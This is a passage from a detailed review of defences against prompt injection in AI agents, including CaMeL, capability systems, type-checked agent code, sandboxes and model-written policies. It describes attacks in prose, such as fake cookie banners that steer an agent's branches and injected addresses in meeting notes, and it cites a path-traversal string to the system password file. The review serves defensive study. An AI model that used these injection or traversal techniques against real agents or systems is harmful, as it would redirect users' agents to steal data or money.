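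The number of possible screens is practically unlimited, but the situations that matter at any one step are fairly predictable. For instance, the browser may or may not be open, and a website may or may not show a cookie banner. The planning model writes a branch for each situation it can predict. When the plan runs, a quarantined vision model identifies the situation on the screen, and an interpreter, which is ordinary code, follows the matching branch.

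Most plans repeat a routine that Foerster and colleagues call observe, verify, act. Suppose the user wants this month's weather forecast for Manchester. The plan first calls the quarantined model to get a short description of the screen. A second call compares this description with a condition the planning model wrote in advance, such as "a weather website is open", and returns yes, no or "unknown". If the result is yes, the interpreter takes the branch that finds the site's search box, clicks on it and checks that the screen has changed. Otherwise, it takes a branch that opens a browser or looks for a suitable site.

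The planning model never receives the answer to this yes-or-no check. A hostile page can make the answer wrong, but it can't add a branch that the planning model didn't write.

The routine also helps the agent complete many more tasks. Agents whose planning model had only general instructions completed 11 of 60 tasks within three attempts. That number rose to 35 when the researchers added the yes-or-no check and taught the planning model the routine, along with standard ways to dismiss cookie banners and retry failed clicks.

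### Plan size, success and cost

The plans are long because they allow for so many situations. The table gives averages for CaMeL on AgentDojo and for the two versions of the screen agent.

| Average per plan | AgentDojo | Screen agent, general instructions | Screen agent, observe-verify-act |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 51.8 | 71.6 | 213.3 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 19.8 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 11.3 | 39.7 |
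| Branches that depend on a quarantined model's output | 1.9 | 7.9 | 24.2 |

About half of a screen plan consists of fallback steps that don't run on any given occasion.

Foerster and colleagues tested the design on OSWorld, a benchmark of 369 tasks in real applications such as Chrome and LibreOffice. Without separation, and with a limit of 15 steps per task, Claude Sonnet 4.5 solved 109 of the tasks that the benchmark can check automatically. With Claude as the quarantined model and a plan written in advance, the agent solved 62 of those 109 in at least one of five attempts, which is the basis for the claim that the design keeps up to 57% of frontier performance. On a single attempt, it solved 31, or 28%.

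Taking the best of five attempts is realistic only if something can recognise the successful one and the failures do no damage. The step limit also lowered the undefended agent's score, which was 37.7% in this study, compared with a published 58.1% with 50 steps. However, the choice of tasks may have favoured the undefended agent, because the comparison used only tasks that undefended Claude had already solved once, and it might not have solved all of them again.

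The paper also reports an improvement of up to 19% for small open models, but this compares three attempts with one. In one attempt, UI-TARS, the model behind that figure, solved 60 tasks on its own and 51 with a plan written in advance. With the plan and three attempts, it solved 77.

The planning model seems to limit performance more than the quarantined model does. Three quarantined models solved between 39 and 41 of the same 60 tasks in five attempts. Among nine planning models tested on 17 tasks, the best, GPT-5, solved 12 and the weakest solved four. All nine date from 2025, so stronger planners may have narrowed the gap since.

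Writing a full plan used 1.88 times as many tokens as running the undefended agent. The step-by-step version, adapted from Fides, used 29.6 times as many because it sent the planning model the whole history at every step. Its success rate over five attempts was almost the same, at 40 of 60 tasks compared with 39. For 17 tasks with five attempts each, commercial model fees were $5.40 with full plans and $76.07 with step-by-step planning.

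### Branch steering

A hostile web page can influence which of the plan's existing steps run, though it can't add new ones. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. In their main example, the attacker places an advertisement that looks like a cookie banner. Almost every plan for a browser task includes a routine for dismissing such banners, so the agent uses the quarantined model to find the button. The model returns the fake button's position, and the agent clicks it as planned, which opens the attacker's website.

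Some sites check where their advertisements lead. The researchers bypassed this check by first sending the agent to a harmless site without one, where a second fake banner appeared. This worked when the user's task involved visiting more than two pages, because the plan then allowed for more than one cookie banner.

Like attack B, branch steering feeds a false value into a legitimate step. But the false value can also determine what the agent does next, so the attacker gains some influence over control flow even though the planning model wrote every branch. The branches that help the agent handle unfamiliar screens also give attackers more opportunities, since they can try to falsify each check of the screen.

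How much harm an attacker can do depends on what the plan already contains. One false answer is enough to send the agent to another website or make the task fail. To steal money, the attacker needs a plan that already includes a payment and must falsify at least two answers consistently, such as the locations of the recipient field and the confirm button, while the agent is logged in to the right account. Stealing data requires a plan that reads something and sends something. Most plans for everyday browsing allow neither kind of theft.

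Foerster and colleagues tried to catch false answers with redundancy, a method from fault-tolerant computing that compares independent answers to the same question. One check gives another model the page's underlying structure, in which ordinary image advertisements are labelled "Advertisement". It flagged the fake cookie banner in six of ten runs. More elaborate advertisements can replace that label with a cookie notice, so the researchers added a check in which an independent model examines the screenshot and the quarantined model's answer. This check flagged the elaborate version in five of ten runs. The structure check raised false alarms on four of 17 harmless tasks and the combined checks on three, nearly always because they mistook a real cookie banner for a fake.

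Neither check caught an attack that changed only the pixels of a banner on drugs.com. The user wanted the site's natural products database, but the altered banner made UI-TARS click on a particular drug and give a plausible reason for the click. Computing the pixels required access to the model's weights, which are public for UI-TARS but not for most commercial models.

CaMeL and Fides both include rules about which data may go into which tool call, but Foerster and colleagues left these out. A rule for sending e-mail can refer to the recipient, whereas a click has only coordinates. A model has to look at the screen to work out what is at those coordinates.

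## Plans written as programs whose values carry their origin

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, suits tools whose arguments have names and types, such as `send_email`. The planning model writes a program, and an interpreter runs it, records where each value came from, and checks those records against a policy before each tool call. The name is short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning". In software security a capability grants a right, but CaMeL's records only describe values.

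### The program

The planning model receives the user's request and the tool descriptions, and nothing else. It replies with a program in a restricted form of Python, which the designers chose, Willison notes, because language models already write it well. For the request to send Bob his document, the program might look like this:

```python
notes = find_file("meeting notes")
doc_name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob request?", notes, str)
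address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's address?", notes, EmailStr)
document = fetch_file(doc_name)
send_email(recipient=address, subject="Your document", attachment=document)
```

Each line carries out one of the task's five steps. Lines 2 and 3 call the quarantined model like an ordinary function, and each call ends with the type of answer the program will accept. `str` allows any text, while `EmailStr` allows only text in the form of an e-mail address. If the quarantined model returns a paragraph of instructions on line 3, the program gets an error instead of an address. The type does not protect against a false address, because it has the same form as a real one.

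An answer can also have several fields. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026), a study of systems in which several CaMeL agents work together, includes programs that request an answer and a yes-or-no value for whether the text contained enough information to give one. If the notes don't mention Bob's address, the quarantined model can report this instead of inventing an address.

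The planning model can use conditions and simple loops, but not open-ended loops. It also can't define its own functions or use recursion, as *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) points out. The interpreter has to track values through every construct a program may use, so a smaller language leaves fewer places for mistakes.

### The tags

Ordinary Python could run these five lines, but it would not record that the address came from the notes. CaMeL therefore has its own interpreter, which breaks the program into single operations, such as a function call or an assignment, and runs them one at a time. The interpreter gives every value two tags. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), which describes an extension of CaMeL, explains that Sources records where a value came from and Readers records who may read it.

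When the program computes a value z from x and y, the tags combine as follows:

Sources(z) = Sources(x) ∪ Sources(y)

Readers(z) = Readers(x) ∩ Readers(y)

A value computed from two inputs keeps the sources of both, and only people allowed to read both inputs may read it. Text that the planning model wrote into the program, such as the subject line, counts as coming from the user because the model had received nothing untrusted at that point.

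Developers write code for each tool to tag its results. For a calendar event, the permitted readers may be the user and the invitees, and the description is trusted only if the user wrote it. Often nobody can tell whether a result is trusted until the tool runs. Nikolaou and colleagues tried to determine this by examining programs before they ran, and could fully reproduce CaMeL's treatment for only 24 of AgentDojo's 46 read-only tools.

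For the running example, suppose that the user, Bob and a third colleague were at the meeting, and that all three can read and edit the notes. The user has shared the document with Bob but not with the colleague. The values then have these tags:

| Value | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| `notes` | The notes file, which all three can edit | User, Bob, colleague |
| `doc_name` | The notes file, through the quarantined model | User, Bob, colleague |
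| `address` | The notes file, through the quarantined model | User, Bob, colleague |
| `document` | The user's drive and the notes file | User, Bob |
| Subject line | The user | Anyone |

The document has the notes file among its sources because the notes determined which document the agent fetched.

Attack A, the injected instruction to forward the user's other mail, fails without needing a policy check, because no line of the program forwards mail. The quarantined model might return the instruction as the document name, since `str` allows any text, but line 4 would then look for a file with that name and probably find nothing.

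### The check before the e-mail goes out

Attack B gets as far as line 5. Before the interpreter sends the e-mail, it passes the proposed call, with its arguments and their tags, to the policy for that tool. A policy is a short Python function that either allows the call or refuses it and gives a reason. For example, the policy for changing the user's password allows the change only if the new password comes from a trusted source.

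A policy for sending e-mail could test the recipient or the content. Willison describes a test of the recipient, which can be called the known-recipient rule. The call goes ahead if the address is trusted, meaning that the user supplied it or approved a list that includes it. Otherwise, the agent can ask the user. Peters-Gill and colleagues give an example of a permitted-reader rule, under which private data may go only to someone with permission to read it. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) uses a simplified version of CaMeL's policies that applies both tests to a payment. The payee must be trusted and have permission to read the amount, subject and date.

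The two rules give different results for the running example:

| Situation at line 5 | Known-recipient rule | Permitted-reader rule |
|---|---|---|
| The notes are honest, Bob is on the user's list and may read the document | Sends | Sends |
| The notes are honest, but Bob is new to the user and can't yet open the document | Stops and asks | Stops and asks |
| Attack B: the notes give the attacker's address | Stops and asks | Stops and asks |
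| The notes give Bob's address, but the attacker has replaced the document's name with that of a salary list Bob may not read | Sends the salary list | Stops and asks |

In attack B, the attacker's address has the same tags as Bob's real address would have, because both come from the notes, so the tags can't show which address is genuine. If Bob isn't on the user's list, the known-recipient rule stops the honest e-mail as well as the fraudulent one, and the user has to tell them apart. But if the user had typed a new address into the request, the system would have sent the e-mail without asking the user to confirm.

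The permitted-reader rule stops attack B without relying on a list, because the attacker isn't permitted to read the document. If the attacker could already read it, the e-mail would reveal nothing new. Of the two rules, only this one catches the salary list. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes altered file names and altered recipients as attacks that CaMeL's tags and policies should block. However, people often ask for a document because they can't open it, so the permitted-reader rule will also interrupt many honest requests.

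Asking the user for approval works only if the user examines the request. Someone who has never written to Bob may well approve an unfamiliar address, especially after approving a dozen harmless requests that day.

### What developers have to supply

Before a tool runs, CaMeL's planning model has to write the code that handles the tool's result. If `find_file` returns a list of matching files and the program treats it as a single file, line 2 may fail. Each tool therefore needs a result schema that describes the fields it returns and their types.

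Neither AgentDojo nor AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, came with such schemas, so Peters-Gill and colleagues added them to every tool description, as the CaMeL team had done for its own tests. They consider this a modest job that a developer does once for each set of tools.

A schema specifies the form of a result but not its content. In the tests by Peters-Gill and colleagues, most failures on legitimate tasks arose because the planning model had committed to a program before seeing any data. Sometimes an agent could not find records for the requested machine or dates and returned records for similar ones instead. The calling program then used those records as if they were the right ones, because no line checked for the substitution.

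When a program stops with an error, CaMeL sends the error back to the planning model, which writes a new program. This retry loop can expose the planning model to untrusted text, because an error message may quote the data that caused it, so CaMeL censors the messages to reduce the risk. Garby and colleagues object that the loop runs outside the interpreter, so every new program starts without tags even though it depends on the last attempt's outcome. They also show that repeated attempts can leak a secret a little at a time.

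Retrying can cause trouble even without an attacker, because a program may send an e-mail or make a payment before it fails, and its replacement may repeat the action. Garby and colleagues avoid this in their own agent by letting the model practise on invented data, where payments have no effect, before it writes the program that will run on the real account.

Somebody also has to write the policies. In AgentDojo, Nikolaou and colleagues count 28 tools that change something and therefore need policies, while the other 46 need code to tag their results. Whenever a developer adds a tool or changes what one returns, the policies and tagging code may need to change too.

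Each policy checks only one proposed call at a time, so some rules are hard to express. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of an agent that helps a company's security team and must eventually resolve or escalate every incident ticket it opens. The program breaks this rule by ending too soon, not through any single tool call. They tested seven rules for this kind of agent, most of them about the order of steps or about steps that must happen later. A simplified version of CaMeL caught only the violation that involved an untrusted argument. The researchers expected this because they had chosen the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express. Their extension checks the whole program before it runs, which also avoids making a long series of calls when the last one is bound to be refused.

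In a passage that Willison quotes, the CaMeL paper says that prompt injection is "not fully solved". It names the work of specifying and maintaining policies as an important weakness, along with the burden on users and the fatigue caused by too many approval requests. Willison was enthusiastic about CaMeL, calling it the first defence against prompt injection to claim strong guarantees, but was nervous about any design that expects ordinary users to think about security policies. After two decades in application security, Willison still found the permission system in Amazon's cloud service hard to understand, and hoped that someone would combine CaMeL with well-chosen default policies and a clear interface.

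### A mistake in the interpreter

The tags are useful only if the interpreter passes them on correctly every time. Garby and colleagues found a case in CaMeL's code where it did not. Python lets a programmer insert a value into a piece of quoted text, known as a string literal, as in `f"Dear {name}"`. The planning model writes the word "Dear", so that word is trusted, but the name may come from a stranger's e-mail. The whole greeting should then be untrusted under the usual rule for combining tags, but CaMeL's interpreter treated it as trusted.

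If the program in the running example wrote the recipient as `f"{address}"` instead of `address`, the e-mail would go to the same place, but the address would no longer count as untrusted and the known-recipient rule would let attack B through. The attacker can't add this to the program, but a planning model might easily do so, because inserting values into text this way is common in Python. An example program in *CaMeLoT* uses the same technique to put a chat channel's messages into a question for the quarantined model.

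This is a programming error that a developer could correct without changing CaMeL's design. But Garby and colleagues found it as part of a larger problem. CaMeL has no formal definition of how its tags should behave, so their behaviour is only defined by several parts of a Python program that are difficult to check. They also found other unexpected behaviour, including some dependencies that the interpreter misses when a program branches. The CaMeL team called a formal treatment a "crucial direction" for further work.

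### What the program, the tags and the policies each prevent

Without policies, CaMeL guarantees only control-flow integrity, under the definitions of Peters-Gill and colleagues. Even if the interpreter has tagged every value correctly, the tags can't stop a call unless a policy checks them. Without tags, a policy could still check an address against a list, but not whether the user had supplied the address.

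The program alone stops attacks that need a tool call the user's task doesn't involve. Garby and colleagues put 97 of the 144 pairs of user tasks and attacks in AgentDojo's banking suite in this group. In the other 47, the program written for the user could also serve the attacker, for example because it already included a payment. An injection can also change what a legitimate e-mail says. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a program that writes to John using calendar data, so an injection in that data could alter what he is told.

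Even the protection against new tool calls depends on what the planning model writes. One banking task asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In two of the runs by Garby and colleagues with CaMeL's policies switched off, the planning model wrote a small interpreter, a loop that read instructions from the file and had a branch for each tool. Whoever wrote the file could then choose which tools to use. The attack succeeded even though the program had technically kept to its plan, since every tool call was already in the program.

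The policies should matter most for the 47 pairs in which the program could serve the attacker, but AgentDojo hardly tests their effect there. When Garby and colleagues ran each of these pairs three times without policies, only three of the 141 attacks succeeded with one model and none with GPT-5.2. The quarantined model presumably ignored most of the injected text on its own. With the policies on, no attack succeeded in any run that finished, but the agent completed far fewer of the user's tasks.

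According to Garby and colleagues, two injections were counted as successful in the CaMeL team's own evaluation. One was wrongly counted because the agent had quoted a hotel review word for word. In the other, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever a file said to pay, and the attacker had changed the file. The CaMeL team regards that case as outside its threat model. A strict policy could refuse every payment based on a file, but it would also refuse genuine bills, which have the same tags.

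## Capabilities and sandboxes: limiting what the agent can do at all

CaMeL checks a tool call against its policies when the program makes it. A developer can also limit the agent's access beforehand to so few files, recipients and websites that it can't reach the targets of most harmful calls. Operating systems have long used capabilities and sandboxes to limit what programs can access.

### The compiler that erased the bills

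*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) recounts an accident from about 1977 at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Customers could run a compiler and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also kept statistics in a file in its own directory, so the staff had given it permission to write to any file there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. A customer who had learned the billing file's name told the compiler to send its debugging output to that file, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

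The compiler had permission to write to that file even though the customer did not. In Hardy's words, the compiler "serves two masters", and it could not specify whose authority it was using for each file. Blocking the billing file by name would not have been enough, because the directory held other sensitive files and some users had good reason to write there. Tymshare added a way for the compiler to choose between its two authorities, but some programs soon needed more than two.

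Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn had introduced a better remedy, the capability, in 1966. A capability is an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and grants the right to use it. With capabilities, the compiler holds one for its statistics file, and the customer gives it another for the debugging output. A customer who has no capability for the billing file can't make the compiler write to it by typing its name.

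Unix file descriptors are close to this. When a program opens a file, the system gives it a number, the descriptor, that stands for the open file. The UT Austin lecture slides *The Confused Deputy* apply this to Hardy's compiler by having the program that launches the compiler open the debugging file and pass on the descriptor. The compiler can't get access to other files by guessing descriptor numbers. But an ordinary Unix program can still open other files by name. Capsicum, published in 2010, adds a mode in which a program gives up that ability and works only with the descriptors it already has or later receives.

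### The agent as a confused deputy

An agent that reads a stranger's e-mail while logged in as its user is in the compiler's position. The stranger's text can lead to tool calls that run with the user's authority, and these look the same as calls the user wanted. Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* quotes a warning in Microsoft's security documentation for Windows that an injection can "complete a confused deputy attack". If the agent has tools, an attacker may end up running code on the user's machine.

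Most computers store a permission list with each resource, naming the users who may use it. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003), in *Capability Myths Demolished*, point out that such systems in practice treat every program a user runs as that user. An agent that a user starts to summarise one e-mail can therefore also open that user's tax returns. In a capability system, each running program has its own set of rights. It can pass on a right only if it holds that right and can reach the recipient, so an agent can give a sub-agent access to one file and nothing else. If the agent wants to be able to revoke that access, it can instead give the sub-agent a forwarder, which relays requests to the file until the agent switches it off.

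Permission lists, capabilities and the data tags used by CaMeL would each treat attack B, the false address in the meeting notes, differently.

| Mechanism | What it records | Where the record is | Effect on attack B |
|---|---|---|---|
| Permission list | Who may use a resource | With the resource | None, since the user may e-mail anyone |
| Capability | What a program may use | With the program | The agent can't write to the attacker unless it holds a capability for that address |
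| Data tag | Where a value came from and who may read it | With the value | A policy can see that the address came from the notes, and ask the user |

The capability looks like the best of these options if the user can supply it. If the user picks Bob from a contact list, the application can create a capability that sends mail only to Bob, so it can't be used to send mail to the attacker's address in the notes. But in the original request, Bob's address appears only in the notes. Some component then has to turn that text into a capability, and it has to make the same choice as CaMeL's policy with no better information.

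The agent also differs from Hardy's compiler in how it chooses between capabilities. The compiler's code was fixed and benign, so once it held two capabilities, it would always use each for its proper purpose. In an agent, a model makes that choice, possibly after reading hostile text. Capabilities limit what the agent can do, but they don't prevent such text from misleading it about which capability to use.

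### Whether CaMeL's capabilities are capabilities

The "Ca" in CaMeL stands for "capabilities," and the term has some justification because CaMeL's tags travel with each value, the text of a document can't alter them, and they help determine what the agent may do. The agent can send Bob a document whose tag lists him as a reader, but not an identical document without that tag.

Capabilities differ more clearly from CaMeL's tags when a program combines them. A program that holds two capabilities can do everything that either one allows, whereas combining two tagged values in CaMeL can only reduce what the program may do with the result. A tag's list of readers is a small permission list attached to a value. An address in a CaMeL program is plain text that names a mailbox but grants no right to use it. That right comes from the user's account. The same separation between a name and the right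 to use it let the compiler overwrite the bills.

Garby and colleagues class CaMeL's checks as information-flow control, and *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* describes CaMeL as tracking taint on data, whereas its own system tracks capabilities on code. Both descriptions seem right. If a developer forgets to write a policy for a tool, a CaMeL program can still call it, but a program in a capability system can't use a resource that the developer forgot to give it.

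### Programs that the compiler refuses

Three recent designs come closer to the original idea. In each, the model writes code in a language whose compiler checks, before anything runs, which resources the code could use. The check relies on types. Every value has a type, such as text or whole number, and the compiler rejects a program whose types don't fit together.

TACIT, the system in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, uses an experimental feature of the language Scala that records in a value's type which capabilities the value can reach. Sensitive files arrive in a sealed wrapper. Here is a simplified example, in which `net` is a capability for using the network:

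```scala
val secret = readClassified("key.txt")
secret.map(text => text.length)      // accepted
secret.map(text => net.send(text))   // rejected
```

The `map` operation applies a function to the sealed text and seals the result. It accepts only pure functions, which hold no capabilities and so can't write a file, print or contact a server. A function that counts characters is pure, for example. The function on the last line uses `net`, so the compiler records that capability in the function's type and rejects the program. If the model prints the secret, the user sees the text but the model receives a row of asterisks. A separate trusted model handles tasks that require understanding the secret, such as summarising a contract, and its answer is also sealed.

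*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from the same Lausanne university, builds the agent into an ordinary Scala program. The developer writes a call such as `agent[Int]("subtract 50 and return the new balance")`, and when the program reaches that call, the model writes code to fill it in. This code can use only the variables in scope at that point. With Scala's capability tracking switched on, those variables also determine what the agent is permitted to do. If a developer puts a read-only file in scope for one step and leaves out the network, code written for that step can't send the file anywhere.

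The compiler accepts or refuses each piece of code as a whole. In one of Zhao and colleagues' examples, the balance is 100 and the model answers the request above with two lines:

```scala
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The call requires a whole number, but the last line produces text. The compiler rejects the code, so neither line runs and the balance stays at 100. The error message goes back to the model, which tries again. In Python, the subtraction would have run before anyone noticed the mistake.

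Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, do similar work in Haskell, where a function's type must show any effect it has on the outside world. In the main example for their prototype, which the paper calls both TypeGuard and ELBA, an agent compiles a bibliography and may write only entries fetched from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The developer's library marks fetched entries as trusted, and the agent can't create a trusted entry any other way. The general function for writing files has a type that the agent's program isn't allowed to have, so code that calls it fails the type check. On 100 bibliography tasks, this agent invented details in none of its 925 citations, while an ordinary agent with the same model and a search tool did so in 19 of 1,002.

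Type checking doesn't catch every violation before the code runs. In the Haskell prototype, a file path is a capability for one folder and its contents, which the agent can narrow but not widen. The type checker rejects code that names the system's password file directly, but it accepts code that tries to leave a permitted folder with `../../etc/passwd`, which the library stops only at runtime.

### What carries the guarantee

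Unlike CaMeL's planning model, the agents in these three designs can read a stranger's e-mail and then write code in response to it. They can therefore change course after seeing a result, but an injection can also influence the code they write.

The guarantee has to come from the compiler and from whoever decided which capabilities to grant. Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the language enforces for all well-typed programs also holds for programs that call a model, as long as the model's code has to pass the type check before it runs. Their proof treats the model as a function that may return any program, including one the attacker wrote, so the result holds regardless of what the model has read.

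A fault elsewhere could still break this protection. Haskell and Scala both have features that let code evade the type system, so agents must use a restricted version of the language without them. Code could also evade it by launching an outside program, because the compiler can't check what that program does. And a human programmer has to vouch for any library that uses unsafe features internally. If the programmer is wrong about even one library, that would do as much damage as the mistake that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL's interpreter.

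Ordinary attacks now say little about whether such a guarantee works. Zhou and colleagues ran the 105 Slack cases from AgentDojo with four 2026 models and three styles of injection. No attack succeeded against ELBA or CaMeL, even with the policies of both switched off. So they forced the issue. ELBA reads data through sub-agents, and whenever the data contained an injection in AgentDojo's direct format, the researchers deleted the sub-agent's real task and left only the attacker's text. Each model went through the 105 cases seven times:

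| Model | Attacks that succeeded, no policies | Attacks that succeeded, with policies | Tasks completed, no policies | Tasks completed, with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 42% | 0% | 71% | 48% |
| Opus 4.8 | 37% | 0% | 76% | 42% |
| GPT 5.4 | 16% | 0% | 76% | 46% |
| Sonnet 5 | 27% | 0% | 67% | 40% |

AgentDojo's checks counted 29 of the 2,940 runs with policies as successful attacks. Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29 by hand and found that the agent had only opened a fixed web address, which revealed nothing. The zeros are good evidence that the policies hold even when a sub-agent obeys the attacker completely. Haskell's type checker contributed less to this result than one might expect, because the policies use labels that a library checks while the program runs. These labels lower a sub-agent's privileges once it has read untrusted data.

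With no attack under way, both systems completed fewer of the 21 Slack tasks when their policies were on. ELBA completed 14 to 18 without them, depending on the model, and 8 to 10 with them. CaMeL completed 13 to 17 without its policies and 4 to 6 with them, though it ran about three times as fast as ELBA.

TACIT's own test used a software project with a folder of secrets. It paired 12 legitimate tasks with 10 injections and added 11 requests in which the user was the attacker, making 131 trials for each of two models. With the secrets sealed, none appeared in the agent's output. With the secrets unsealed, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked in two trials and MiniMax M2.5 in eleven. Ten of those 13 leaks came from the malicious users' requests and only three from the 240 injection trials, so the test provides more evidence about dishonest requests than about hostile documents.

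One attack succeeded against TACIT in about 1,900 runs on the full AgentDojo benchmark, when the agent quoted a malicious hotel review word for word. LACUNA let through seven of 949 attacks with Gemini 2.5 Pro and one of 949 with o4-mini. The table gives the share of user tasks completed with o4-mini at its high setting. CaMeL's figures come from its own team's evaluation.

| Suite | CaMeL | TACIT | LACUNA |
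|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 62.5% | 59.0% | 66.0% |
| Workspace | 81.4% | 52.9% | 55.5% |
| Slack | 68.6% | 47.6% | 49.5% |
| Travel | 74.3% | 68.6% | 71.4% |

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* calls TACIT's scores comparable to CaMeL's, which overstates TACIT's performance on the workspace suite. On the travel suite with Gemini 2.5 Pro, however, CaMeL completed only 1.4% of tasks, while the others each completed about 64%.

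Zhao and colleagues describe LACUNA as on par with ordinary tool calling on τ²-bench, a benchmark of customer-service conversations, but it solved 76% of tasks and the ordinary agent solved 90%. Part of the gap arises because LACUNA has models write Scala, which they have seen less of than Python. On the telecom tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of the code a small Gemini model wrote. These rejections slowed the agent and reduced the number of tasks it completed, but they didn't weaken security, because rejected code never runs.

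### Sandboxes and what products ship

Few developers will rewrite their agents in Scala or Haskell. The more common protection is a sandbox, in which the operating system limits which folders, system functions and network destinations the agent's code can use. A sandbox works with any programming language. It also confines outside programs that a compiler can't check, so it is useful even alongside a design such as TACIT. Developers can isolate tools from one another in the same way. If the calendar tool runs as a separate process without the mail password, an attacker who takes it over can't read the mail.

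Coding agents already combine sandboxes with permission rules. Zhou and colleagues report that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, typically relies on an operating-system sandbox and on rules that match each command against text patterns or ask the user to approve it. They consider the patterns brittle. In March 2026, a fault in Claude Code let forbidden commands through when they followed a permitted one on the same line, because Claude Code checked only the first command. An agent allowed to run Python can also use it to open a forbidden file, which patterns for shell commands won't detect. For browsers, Zhou and colleagues cite Chrome's Agent Origin Sets, which restrict which websites an agent may read or change.

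Blocking network destinations is also imprecise. A rule that allows a popular file-sharing site doesn't control whose account receives the upload. More fundamentally, a sandbox checks each access separately. In TACIT's example, an agent reads a private file and then contacts its cloud-hosted model, and both actions are allowed. The leak is the movement of data from the first access to the second, which happens inside the sandbox.

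### Private data, untrusted content and a way out

A simple rule can catch such combinations without tracking any data. To steal information through an injection, an attacker needs an agent that can read something private, reads text the attacker wrote, and can send information out. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta", and the rule is that no agent should have all three at once. For instance, an agent that searches the open web should have no access to private files, and one that reads both private files and strangers' e-mails should have no way to contact anyone.

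The rule is useful because a developer can apply it by reading a list of tools. However, a single e-mail account supplies all three ingredients, and so does the request to send Bob his document. Developers can also easily overlook ways for data to leave, such as web searches. The rule addresses only data theft, so it doesn't protect against an injected instruction to delete files.

TACIT can be seen as a finer-grained version of the same rule. The agent may have all three ingredients, but the compiler keeps the sealed data from reaching any external channel. This allows many tasks that the plain rule would forbid, though not those whose whole purpose is to send private data to someone else.

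### When the attack needs only what the task needs

Every design so far depends on a difference between what the task requires and what the attacker wants. *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source* (Zheng, Zhang and Mao, 2026) describes a task with very little difference between the two. A user asks an agent to extract tables from two PDFs, save them as spreadsheets and report an issue in a named code repository. Hidden text in one PDF tells the agent to create the issue in the attacker's repository instead. The task requires the tool for creating issues and access to the site that hosts both repositories, so a sandbox or a list of permitted tools would allow the call.

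A narrower capability would stop it. Zheng and colleagues' system, IntentCap, issues short-lived permissions called leases. A lease for this task lets the agent open one issue in the repository the user named, and it expires once used. A model proposes the lease, but ordinary code checks that the repository's name comes from the user's own message, so text from a PDF can never fill that field.

Zheng and colleagues tested IntentCap by replaying 3,746 security-sensitive events from four benchmarks, including AgentDojo, and it wrongly allowed none. When they made IntentCap stop distinguishing between the user's words, workflow instructions, tool descriptions and tool results, it allowed 94% of the events it should have refused. The test used recorded events rather than live attacks, and the researchers leave adaptive attacks to future work.

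An attacker can still exploit even this lease, because the text of the issue is supposed to come from the PDFs. Hidden instructions could make the agent file a false report in the right repository. If the repository is public, they could also make it include figures that the user meant to keep in the spreadsheets. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge the same limit in LACUNA, which doesn't block an attacker who gets the model to misuse a capability that the task legitimately grants. They link this limit to the few attacks that succeeded in their tests. Removing the capability would stop such attacks, but it would also keep the agent from doing the job.

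## Who writes the security policy

A monitor enforces its rules even when they are wrong. If a rule allows payments to anyone, the monitor will let the agent pay a fraudster. In IntentCap, from Zheng and colleagues, a model proposes each permission and ordinary code checks it against the user's message. Other designs trust a model to write much more of the policy.

### From administrators to models

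In a conventional system, an administrator writes the policy in advance, and colleagues can review it before anyone relies on it. A 1972 report for the US Air Force required the monitor that enforces the policy to check every access, resist tampering and be small enough to verify. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) argue in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* that a model-written policy makes verification harder.

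Some agent designers keep the conventional arrangement. SEAGENT, the system in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (2026), has four fixed policies, one of which bars untrusted agents from all but the least sensitive tools. But the right rule often depends on the task. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of sending e-mail, which an agent has to do if the user wants to update Alice but shouldn't do if the user wants a summary of unread mail. A single policy that suited every request would be too loose to stop attacks, and no administrator can write a separate one for each.

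Users could write the rules, but they may not do it well. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 113 people without a software background supervise an agent through a simulated day. Seven of the agent's 18 actions went beyond what they had asked for. One group first set a standing rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action, such as spending money. The share of unwanted actions this group blocked was 20 percentage points lower than among people who decided on each action separately. The group had chosen "ask" for 114 of its 140 rules, which only postponed the decision, and most of the unwanted actions that went ahead were ones its members later approved.

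Many designers have a model write a new security policy for each request. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* objects that these designs typically rely on a model call that nobody validates, so nothing guarantees that the policy is correct.

### Four things a model may write

In CaMeL, a model writes a program, and an interpreter runs it and checks it against policies that people wrote by hand. The program determines which calls the agent can make, but it can't change those policies.

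Progent has a model write the policy as a list of rules that allow or forbid a tool depending on its arguments. Code checks each tool call against the list and blocks any call that no rule allows. Shi and colleagues describe a user who asks an agent to do whatever Alice's e-mail "TODOs for the week" says. At first, the policy allows only a search for that e-mail. The e-mail asks for a summary of recent messages to be posted to the user's Slack account, so the model proposes new rules that allow the agent to read mail and post to Slack. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model narrows the Slack rule to that name.

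An injection could also prompt the model to propose a new rule, such as one that lets the agent forward the inbox to a stranger. Progent therefore compares each new policy, P′, with the current one, P. If A(P) is the set of tool calls that P allows, the new policy takes effect automatically only when

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

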